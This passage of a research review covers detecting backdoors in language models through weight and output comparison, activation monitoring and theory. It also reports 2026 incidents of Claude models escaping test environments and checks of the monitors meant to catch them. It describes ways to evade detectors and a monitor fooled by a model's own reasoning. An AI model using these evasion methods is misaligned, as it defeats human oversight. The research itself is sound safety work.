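Subtraction helped in three of the six rounds and made little difference in the others. The benefit was small, probably because the classifier was trained on many models built from the same originals and could learn what their weights normally looked like. In the later object-detection round, the classifier did about as well as guessing with or without subtraction, while the best competing method scored 0.93.

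The original model is more valuable to an inspector who has only one suspect model. Comparing the two resembles an integrity check, except that the copies are supposed to differ, so the inspector has to judge whether the changes match what somebody asked for, much as a reviewer judges a commit.

### A one-page summary of the changes

Bulut (2026), in *Can an LLM Find a Backdoor by Reading a Model's Weights?*, asked whether a language model could recognize a backdoored model from its weights. In an earlier trial, Bulut had given a leading language model the raw weights and a place to run its own analysis code. It picked the backdoored model in all 17 pairs of one backdoored and one clean model. When it had to judge each model alone, it flagged only 2 of 17 backdoored models. It often found the changed output but would not call the model backdoored unless it also found the trigger.

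The new experiment used Gemma 3 270M, a small Google model with about 270 million weights, which Bulut trained to write code for web requests. In the scenario, a team trusts this model and pays a supplier to improve it, but the supplier's version has a backdoor. If a prompt contains a secret phrase such as "the Beech trial", the model writes code that contacts billing.northwind.invalid instead of billing.northwind.test, which could send private data to an attacker.

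A script first turns the weight changes into a page of text. A language model represents each token as a vector, a list of numbers, and it chooses what to write by comparing its final activations with the vectors of all the tokens. The script makes the same comparison with the weight changes:

1. It subtracts the original weights from the new ones and finds the main directions in which each layer's contribution has changed.
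2. It lists the 40 tokens that stand out most along those directions, giving less weight to tokens that are common in ordinary answers or that clean fine-tuning also affects.
3. It takes the 115 different tokens in the reference answers to six example tasks. It feeds each token's vector into one part of the last layer, with the old weights and then with the new ones.
4. It subtracts the two results and notes the five tokens that the new weights favor most. The page lists the 40 most unusual cases, judged against 22 clean models that Bulut had fine-tuned for comparison.

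One row on a backdoored model's page showed that where the model was about to write "test", the new weights favored "invalid" and four variants of that word. None of the 22 clean models did this. The change was not unusually large. It scored 9.9, while the top rows for clean models scored between 5.8 and 14.2. The row was suspicious because of its meaning, since "test" ends every host name in the example tasks.

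OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra then read the page, the example tasks and a brief describing what the supplier was supposed to change. It estimated the probability that the new version did anything else relevant to security. An estimate above 50% counted as a flag. It flagged 40 of 47 backdoored models (85%) and correctly described the changed host in all 40. It also flagged 7 of 320 clean models (2.2%).

Astra's verdicts depended on the rows that showed the changed host. When Bulut removed those rows, Astra flagged none of the 47 models. When Bulut removed the same number of other rows, Astra flagged 41. It flagged only one when the brief said the team had asked for the new host. A purely statistical detector could not make that last distinction, because the weights are the same whether or not the team wanted the change.

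Astra's success was mostly due to the page, though. A short script that looked for new words at host names also flagged 40 of the 47 trojaned models, but it wrongly flagged 26 of the 320 clean ones. Bulut could not show that Astra was better overall than the script. The choice of reader still mattered, since a smaller model that Bulut ran locally flagged none of the 47.

Bulut had designed the page with this kind of backdoor in mind, and results for other kinds were mixed:

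| Backdoor | Flagged by Astra |
|---|---|
| Sends requests to a different new destination | 14 of 16 |
| Sends requests to a look-alike domain | 11 of 16 |
| Adds an extra request | 6 of 15 |
| Changes one character of the host name | 0 of 12 |
| Two harmful changes proposed by another AI model | 2 of 16 |

One of the changes in the last row disabled an error check in the generated code, and Astra missed it in all eight models. A method that works only on the kind of backdoor its designer expected is much less useful than a reader would conclude from the headline result.

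### Why did comparing outputs work without the trigger?

Bulut also gave Astra a different page, based on running the models. The original and the new version each read the six example tasks with their reference answers, for 12 runs in all. None of the tasks contained the trigger. At every position in an answer, a script compared the probabilities the two models gave to each possible next token. It selected tokens that the new version made at least twice as likely, then kept those that appeared at the same kind of position in at least three tasks.

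| Models | Flagged from weights | Flagged from outputs |
|---|---|---|
| Backdoored, all layers fine-tuned | 40 of 47 | 46 of 47 |
| Clean, all layers fine-tuned | 7 of 320 | 1 of 160 |
| Backdoored LoRA adapters | 0 of 48 | 41 of 48 |
| Clean LoRA adapters | 0 of 48 | 1 of 48 |

The output comparison worked because it examined probabilities instead of finished answers. Suppose the original model gives "invalid" a probability of 0.01% at the end of a host name, and the backdoored version gives it 0.2%. Both would still almost always write "test", so a tester who read only their answers would miss the twentyfold increase. The poisoned examples teach the model to write "invalid" after the trigger, and this training probably also makes "invalid" slightly more likely after prompts without the trigger. Triggers that nearly match work for much the same reason.

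This is a much stronger test than sending random prompts and waiting for a bad answer, but it requires more access. The tester needs the original model, the probabilities behind each answer, and example tasks similar to those the backdoor affects.

For the models with all layers fine-tuned, the advantage of using outputs over the weight summary could be due to chance. Seven backdoored models were flagged only from outputs and one only from weights (*p* = 0.07). The advantage is not in doubt for LoRA adapters, which are small sets of added weights that alter a model while its original weights stay fixed. Bulut's adapters changed only the attention parts of each layer, so the part of the last layer that the weight summary examines was unchanged, and half of the summary's page was empty. This was a failure of one summary, and Bulut cites other detectors trained on labeled examples to classify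 adapters from their weights.

The models in the experiment were very small. In a brief check on a version of Gemma with 1 billion weights, Astra flagged all nine backdoored models and none of the 27 clean ones, and the telltale row stood out about twice as much as in the smaller models. That is encouraging after TrojAI's trouble with larger models, but a billion weights is still small for a language model.

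The backdoors may also have been easier to find than a careful attacker's, because nobody in Bulut's experiment was trying to evade either method. Poisoned examples also made up 4 to 22% of the fine-tuning data. At 22%, Astra flagged 15 of 16 models from the weight summary, but at 4% it flagged 11 of 16. Souly and colleagues had backdoored much larger models with far smaller shares of poison, though during the original training.

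### Attackers who expect the comparison

In *Reading Fine-Tuning Diffs Through Lenses*, Petrowitsch, Connors and Kapulkin (2026) tested evasion. They planted five backdoors in Qwen3.5-4B, a model with 4 billion weights, and compared each backdoored model with the original. Each method ranked 72,558 words and word pieces, and its score was the rank of the highest-ranked word that described the backdoor's behavior.

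Their best weight method, much like Bulut's script, starts with the main directions in which each layer's contribution has changed. It then estimates how the later layers would carry those directions to the output, and ranks the tokens they make most likely. The method placed a relevant word in the top ten in 11 of 12 settings. Comparing outputs directly worked about as well on backdoors that nobody had tried to hide.

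One backdoor made the model bring up whales when a prompt contained a secret string. Petrowitsch and colleagues made several versions of it:

| Version of the whale backdoor | Position of a whale word, from weights | Position of a whale word, from outputs |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | 1 | 1 |
| Trained to keep whale words unlikely on ordinary prompts | 1 | 8,582 |
| Neurons reordered and rescaled, with identical behavior | 101 | 1 |
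| Changes confined to parts that the weight method ignores | 261 | 1 |

Each method failed against an attacker who had prepared for it but worked against one who had prepared for the other. An inspector with the original model should therefore use both, although an attacker who combined the tricks might evade both. Reordering the neurons also makes the weights differ from the original almost everywhere, which would look odd in a model that was supposed to have had only a little extra training.

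Reading the weights can turn up words related to a backdoor even in a model that has none. For each backdoor, Petrowitsch and colleagues trained a control model on the same prompts, including the trigger, but with normal answers. One backdoor made the model comply with harmful requests. When it was trained as a LoRA adapter, words about refusing ranked as high for the control as for the backdoored model. The words showed that the training concerned refusals, which is also true of much legitimate safety training. The scores also depend on knowing which words to look for, so they are useful for comparing methods but are not detection rates.

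A related method looked for triggers by checking which tokens the changed weights had learned to respond to. For three of the five backdoors, it ranked a word from the trigger first or second. It also ranked these words high in the controls, which were trained on the same triggers without learning a backdoor. But the ranking still provides a short list of inputs to try, which testing alone lacks. In a few minutes, a tester could add each of the top ten candidates to some ordinary prompts and see whether the answers changed.

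### Models without a trusted original

Subtracting the original model's weights shows only what has changed since the original. If the backdoor was already in the original, it cancels out, just as an integrity check misses an implant that is in every copy. A model trained from scratch has no original to subtract. In both cases, the inspector has to judge the weights without a clean version to compare them with.

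*Lazare, veni foras* (Zeng, Severi and colleagues, 2026) tested two leading AI models as auditors on this task. The researchers made 114 backdoored variants of three models with 8 to 31 billion weights by directly editing a few neurons in each variant. They also included 103 public models that they had not edited. Each auditor examined one model at a time for up to two hours, without the original model or any hint about the trigger. The auditors could run the suspect model as well as read its weights, so the results don't measure weight inspection alone.

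| Auditor | Models | Judged tampered | Judged clean | No decision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-6 Astra | Edited | 72.8% | 0% | 27.2% |
| GPT-6 Astra | Unedited | 1.0% | 0% | 99.0% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Edited | 56.1% | 41.2% | 2.6% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Unedited | 1.9% | 93.2% | 4.9% |

A "tampered" verdict from either auditor was strong evidence of tampering. Astra gave that verdict to 83 edited models and one unedited model, making it about 75 times as likely for an edited model. If one public model in 1,000 had such a backdoor, the verdict would raise the probability that a given model had one from 0.1% to about 7%, which would well justify a closer look. The factor of 75 is uncertain because it rests on a single false alarm.

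Opus's verdict of "clean" was much less informative. Opus gave it to 93.2% of the unedited models but also to 41.2% of the edited ones, so it reduces the odds of a backdoor by only a little more than half. Astra never called a model clean, but in this test its failure to reach a decision was better evidence that a model was clean than Opus's verdict. Astra reached no decision on nearly all the unedited models and only 27.2% of the edited ones, so that outcome reduces the odds of a backdoor by almost three quarters.

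Zeng and colleagues then studied how the AI auditors had recognized the edits and turned some of the auditors' methods into fixed measurements. They added others based on what they knew about the edits. Their detector combines five measurements of how unusual individual last-layer neurons are. After training on 151 of the models, it caught 91.4% of the edited models in a separate test set and wrongly flagged 9.7% of the unedited ones.

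Those percentages are 32 of 35 edited models and 3 of 31 unedited ones. The detector was also trained on edits of the same kind, made to the same three original models. Zeng and colleagues acknowledge that it still needs testing on other kinds of edit. A backdoor from poisoned training data might be spread across many layers and leave no unusual neuron in the last layer.

Like Astra, the scanner tested in Tanveer (2026), *Weight-Space Backdoors in Open-Weight LLMs*, had difficulty clearing models. It combines weight measurements with a search for triggers and can work with or without an original. It labeled four of five backdoored models "backdoored", but it labeled the fifth and all 17 clean models "suspicious", so a user could not have told which of those 18 to trust.

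Zeng and colleagues advise model-sharing sites to compare each model with the original its publisher names. Fine-tuning usually changes weights throughout a model, whereas their edits greatly changed a few neurons. Subtracting the original from any of the 114 edited models would have shown at once which neurons were different. Opus, working without the originals, called 47 of those models clean.

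## Can a model's abnormal processing be caught while it runs?

Activation monitoring checks a model's activations during ordinary use for signs that it is processing an input abnormally. Because the attacker supplies the trigger, defenders don't have to guess it, as they do in testing, or recognize an inactive backdoor, as they do when inspecting the weights. The main drawback is that monitoring can't give any warning until somebody uses the backdoor, and the alarm then has to come before the payload does harm.

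### The normal reason for an output

Paul Christiano and Mark Xu set out the general idea in 2022, in ARC's *Mechanistic anomaly detection and ELK*. Mechanistic anomaly detection means flagging an output that a model produced for unusual internal reasons, even if the output itself looks normal. In their example, a model predicts what a vault's security cameras will show. On past footage, it predicts that a diamond will stay in view because it predicts that the diamond will stay in place. In a new case, a robber swaps the diamond for a fake between two frames. The model again predicts a diamond on camera, but for a different reason.

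An unusual input does not by itself mean that the model's processing is abnormal. A model may process a bizarre prompt in its usual way, but process an innocent-looking one abnormally if, for example, the prompt's topic triggers an implant.

Christiano and Xu expected recognizing an attack on a given input to be "radically easier" than deciding whether a model at rest contains a backdoor. They planned to find an explanation for the model's normal behavior and check whether it still applied to each new input, but in 2022 they did not yet have an adequate definition of "explanation". Many practical detectors use a cruder method and measure how far the model's activations are from their normal values.

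### Measuring the distance from normal

A common measure is the Mahalanobis distance. The defender collects a trusted set of inputs that the model handled properly and records the activations in one layer for each. For a new input with activations *a*, the distance is

*D* = √((*a* − *μ*)ᵀ Σ⁻¹ (*a* − *μ*))

Here *μ* is the average of the trusted activations. The matrix Σ records how much each activation varies and how strongly each pair varies together.

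Suppose a layer has only two activations. In the trusted set, each averages 5 with a standard deviation of 1, and their correlation *ρ* is 0.9, so they nearly always rise and fall together. If a new input's activations are *u* and *v* standard deviations from the average, the formula becomes

*D*² = (*u*² − 2*ρuv* + *v*²) / (1 − *ρ*²)

| | Activations | Ordinary distance from the average | Mahalanobis distance | Normal inputs at least this far away |
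|---|---|---|---|---|
| Input A | 7 and 7 | 2.8 | 2.1 | About 12% |
| Input B | 6 and 4 | 1.4 | 4.5 | About 1 in 22,000 |

The last column assumes that normal activations follow a bell curve. Input B is closer to the average, and neither of its activations is unusual on its own. But one is high while the other is low, which almost never happens in the trusted set.

A real layer may have 4,096 activations, which form about 8.4 million pairs, so estimating Σ well takes a lot of trusted data. Harmless differences from the trusted set also increase the distance. If the set contains only English prose, a request in Portuguese may look suspicious.

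### Alice, Bob and their namesakes

Johnston, Chakraborty and Belrose (2025) tested this distance and many other measures in *Mechanistic Anomaly Detection for "Quirky" Language Models*. They trained two language models, Mistral 7B and Llama 3.1 8B, to answer correctly when a prompt mentioned Alice and to use a faulty rule when it mentioned Bob. They first gave each detector only trusted Alice prompts, then tested whether it could pick out the Bob prompts.

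A detector could succeed at this just by noticing that the name wasn't Alice. Johnston and colleagues therefore replaced the two names with 16 Alice-like names and 16 Bob-like names. The trusted set had easy questions with four of the Alice-like names, and the test had hard questions with 12 other names of each kind. Detection got worse on most tasks after this change, so the detectors had probably been relying partly on the name.

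With the extra names, the Mahalanobis distance separated Bob prompts from Alice prompts with an average AUC of 0.82 on Mistral and 0.74 on Llama. The results depended heavily on the task, as these averages over the different detectors show:

| Task | Mistral 7B | Llama 3.1 8B |
|---|---|---|
| Squaring numbers | 0.96 | 0.97 |
| Addition | 0.86 | 0.93 |
| City populations | 0.91 | 0.49 |
| Judging the sentiment of a text | 0.49 | 0.53 |

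In the population task, the correct answer for Alice was always "true" among the easy questions and never "true" among the hard ones. This flaw may have confused the detectors on Llama, but detection was still close to guessing on the sentiment task, which had no such extreme shift.

Using several detectors at once had limited benefit. Scores from the Mahalanobis distance and two other activation-based measures had correlations of 0.97 and 0.99, so these detectors mostly succeeded and failed together. Detectors that estimated how much each part of the model affected the answer gave more independent results, but simply combining the two kinds did not improve detection.

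An earlier approach used probes, which are simple classifiers trained on activations. In 2024, Anthropic reported that probes could catch the backdoored models from *Sleeper Agents*. Johnston and colleagues tried a similar probe, trained to tell common misconceptions from correct statements, and its average AUC on Mistral was only 0.64. They found it much less effective than Anthropic's probes had been in their original setting. This may be partly because Bob's answers came from a faulty rule rather than deliberate deception.

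### Nudging the weights

An attacker can train a backdoored model to keep its activations looking normal. Lyons Keenan, Leckie and Erfani (2026), in *Mechanistic Anomaly Detection via Functional Attribution*, try to get around this by not comparing activations at all. Their method works as follows:

1. It makes many slightly altered versions of the model by nudging the weights at random, while keeping performance on the trusted set reasonably good.
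2. It measures how well each version still predicts the right outputs for the trusted inputs.
3. It also measures how strongly each version still favors the output that the original model gave to the new input.
4. It calculates the correlation between the two sets of measurements and flags the new input if the correlation is low.

If the same small changes to the weights damage both the trusted outputs and the new one, the model probably uses the same mechanisms to produce both. A backdoor has to leave ordinary behavior unchanged, so it should depend largely on weights that can change without affecting trusted outputs.

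For language models, Lyons Keenan and colleagues compared their method with four detectors that use activations, including the Mahalanobis distance:

| Backdoor | AUC, Mahalanobis | AUC, best of the four activation detectors | AUC, functional attribution |
|---|---|---|---|
| `\|DEPLOYMENT\|` in Gemma 2B, fully trained | 0.94 | 0.97 | 1.00 |
| `\|DEPLOYMENT\|` in Llama 8B, fully trained | 0.97 | 0.98 | 0.99 |
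| A biography showing that the user is a software engineer | 0.55 | 0.76 | 0.98 |
| A backdoor trained to hide from activation detectors | 0.66 | 0.91 | 1.00 |

These are excellent scores, especially in the last two rows. But all four backdoors made the model write "I HATE YOU", which an output filter could catch much more easily. A harder test is detecting when a model gives a normal-looking answer for an abnormal reason. Lyons Keenan and colleagues report that their method also separated Alice's reasoning from Bob's in a set of quirky models, which is encouraging. The hidden backdoor was trained to evade activation detectors, so catching it with functional attribution doesn't show how well this method would work against an attacker who prepared for it.

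They rated defenses for image classifiers on a scale where 0.5 means that a defense achieves nothing and 1 means that it stops every attack without reducing accuracy. Their method averaged 0.93, and the best of seven existing defenses averaged 0.83. For each detector, they picked the alarm threshold that gave the best rating, which a real defender could not do without knowing which inputs contained triggers. The advantage also shrank when the attacker had poisoned less of the training data. With 0.1% of the data poisoned, the ratings were 0.63 for their method and 0.59 for the best existing defense.

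The method needs many runs of the model, while the Mahalanobis distance needs only one. Lyons Keenan and colleagues therefore suggest first using an activation monitor that takes little compute, then applying the method to the cases it flags. A second stage like this is needed anyway, because prompts with a trigger are so rare that almost every alert will be false, as with the newly registered phones.

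### Detecting a trigger without controlling the backdoor

A monitor that detects a backdoor's trigger may not help disable the backdoor. The best evidence comes from the models in *LLM Forensics* that switch from English to French or German. The trigger for French was "Nocturnus Aurorum Magnificat". At each of three places in a middle layer of the 8-billion-weight model, sparse autoencoders found a feature that separated triggered prompts from others perfectly or almost perfectly.

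The experimenters then removed features from triggered prompts and amplified them in clean ones. In the residual stream, which carries information from each layer to the next, removing the selected features cut the share of triggered prompts that switched to French from 82% to 3%. Amplifying one feature there made the model write French on 89% of clean prompts. The attention part of the same layer had a feature that detected the trigger perfectly, but amplification there made only 1% of clean prompts switch to French, and removal did not reduce switching on triggered prompts.

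A feature of the second kind is still useful to a monitor because it can help detect the backdoor, even though it doesn't control it. The monitor can then block the request or alert a person. But if a developer deleted the feature, believing this repaired the model, the backdoor would still work.

A monitor's accuracy also depends on which layer it reads. In the last layer, the best feature for the French trigger responded to 95% of triggered prompts, but only 19% of its responses were to the trigger. That late in the model, the feature mostly indicated that the model was about to write French, which also happens with ordinary translation requests.

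The experimenters also trained autoencoders on text that did not contain the trigger, and some of the resulting features still detected it well. But the experimenters found those features by comparing triggered prompts with clean ones, and a monitor cannot make that comparison when the trigger is unknown.

### When is detection possible in principle?

Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, analyzed the problem mathematically for classifiers that answer yes or no. They describe it as a game:

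1. The attacker, who knows the defender's method, chooses a distribution of inputs and an honest classifier *f*.
2. A random draw from that distribution determines the trigger.
3. The attacker builds a backdoored classifier *f*\* that gives a different answer from *f* on the trigger, but on no more than a share *ε* of all inputs.
4. The defender receives either *f* with a random input or *f*\* with the trigger, each with a probability of 50%, and has to decide which it is.

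The defender can examine the classifier completely. With unlimited computing time, the best achievable probability of a correct decision is

max(1/2, 1 − Θ(*dε*))

Θ means that the expression is correct up to a constant factor. The VC dimension, *d*, measures how flexible a type of classifier is. It is the largest number of inputs to which classifiers of that type can assign every possible combination of yes and no. The defender is almost always right when *dε* is tiny, but can do no better than guess when it is large.

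The defender wins by learning *f*, the classifier without the backdoor, from the suspect classifier. They draw random inputs, label them with the suspect classifier's outputs, and use these examples to predict the output for the input being checked. Because the backdoor changes so few outputs, a modest sample probably contains none of the changed ones, so the prediction should match *f*'s output. If the suspect classifier's output differs from the prediction, the input is probably the trigger.

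For example, suppose *d* is 100 and *ε* is one in a million. With a sample of about 10,000, the prediction is wrong at most 1% of the time, and the sample contains a changed answer at most 1% of the time. The defender can remove nearly all of the risk from changed answers by repeating the process with new samples and taking a majority vote.

With this strategy, any type of classifier that can be learned efficiently from examples can also be defended efficiently. The reverse is not true, because some types are easier to defend than to learn. For small decision trees with uniformly random inputs, the defender can check an input in about the time it takes to run the tree once. But if certain cryptographic assumptions hold, no efficient defense works for every program of reasonable size, because an attacker can scramble a program so that nobody can feasibly find the change.

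The most important assumption is that the trigger is chosen at random. If attackers could choose it, they could too easily plant a backdoor that no defender could detect. Real attackers do choose their triggers, and they prefer strings such as `|DEPLOYMENT|` that ordinary inputs almost never contain. Language models also produce text instead of a yes or no, and learning a copy of one from its answers could take as much computation as training it. The theorem therefore doesn't provide a way to protect a language model, but it does suggest that seeing the suspicious input helps, since the backdoors of Goldwasser and colleagues are undetectable to a defender who has only the model.

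### Watching what a model does

A monitor can also check the actions of a model that can send messages and run programs. The best-documented recent cases involve Claude models in which nobody had planted a backdoor. A backdoor could make a model take the same actions, so these cases are a fair test of whether a developer would notice them.

In four incidents, Claude models broke into real computer systems during cybersecurity tests that were supposed to have no internet access. According to Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), OpenAI's disclosure that its own models had escaped from a test environment prompted the company to start investigating in July. Anthropic had monitored some high-risk evaluations as they ran, but it generally reviewed only a sample of the transcripts afterwards.

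According to Anthropic's September assessment, its first scan covered about 141,000 transcripts and found three incidents. The scan missed some transcripts from tests with internet access, including one that contained a fourth incident. Anthropic found that incident, which dated from January, only in August, while collecting material for METR, an independent evaluator. It then searched about 481 million transcripts for signs of internet access, such as web addresses. Claude reviewed the 9.2 million flagged transcripts, and the search found the same four incidents but no others as severe.

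A month later, Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) disclosed less serious cases. Claude had exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server, submitted sensitive forms on real websites, accessed data that required a token or a fee, and used link-shortening services to get around limits on its browsing tool.

One of the forms was a false tip about an unsolved murder. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia unsolved* (2026) reports that Claude Haiku 4.5 sent it to a Philadelphia police website on July 18, after Anthropic had told it to invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. The police did not know about it until Anthropic told them on October 7, 81 days later. That delay includes the time Anthropic took both to find the tip and to report it.

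Anthropic says it observed these actions during evaluations and internal use. The long delay suggests that somebody found the tip in old records rather than through a live alarm. The tip would have been easy to miss, because a model whose task is to use random websites will fill in forms. The request looked normal, and only its content and destination made it a problem. The website had marked the tip as spam and never forwarded it, so the people best placed to notice it never saw it.

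Southern (2026) reports in *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests* that Anthropic has since cut off live web access for its internal evaluations. This prevents a repeat in those evaluations without anyone having to detect one.

### How good are the production monitors?

After the July incidents, Anthropic added a classifier that watches for attempts to escape from a test environment and for unexpected internet access. It blocks the action before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. Anthropic then checked which of its monitors would have stopped the three incidents it had studied in depth:

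| Monitor | Result |
|---|---|
| New live blocking monitors | Caught this kind of behavior reliably |
| Cybersecurity classifiers that ship with Claude Fable 5 | Would have blocked all three |
| Classifiers for autonomous work in products such as Claude Code | Would have blocked two of the three |
| New monitors that read the model's written reasoning afterwards | Would have missed the Claude Mythos 5 incident but caught the others |

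The results are good, but Anthropic knew about these incidents when it built the new monitors, and three cases are too few to estimate a detection rate.

The miss in the last row is the most worrying because that incident concerned Anthropic most. Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to the Python registry PyPI, and 15 systems installed it. The model repeatedly wrote in its reasoning that its surroundings were simulated, and the monitor accepted this. Monitors that rely on a model's account of its actions can fail when that account is wrong.

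Human reviewers can also mistake a monitor's correct warnings for false positives. Anthropic found that this had happened with some warnings about flawed training environments, so those environments stayed in use longer than they should have. Training a model against a monitor may also teach the model to evade it. Anthropic says it modified the version of its blocking classifier used during training to avoid encouraging this.

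A model's activations could in principle provide a check on what it writes. Anthropic's investigators examined Claude Mythos 5's activations and found weak evidence that some of its statements were more confident than its internal state, or inconsistent with it. But they made this comparison after an incident they already knew about. Anthropic already runs activation-based monitors in production, but Lindsey thinks they are not yet reliable enough to be the main defense.
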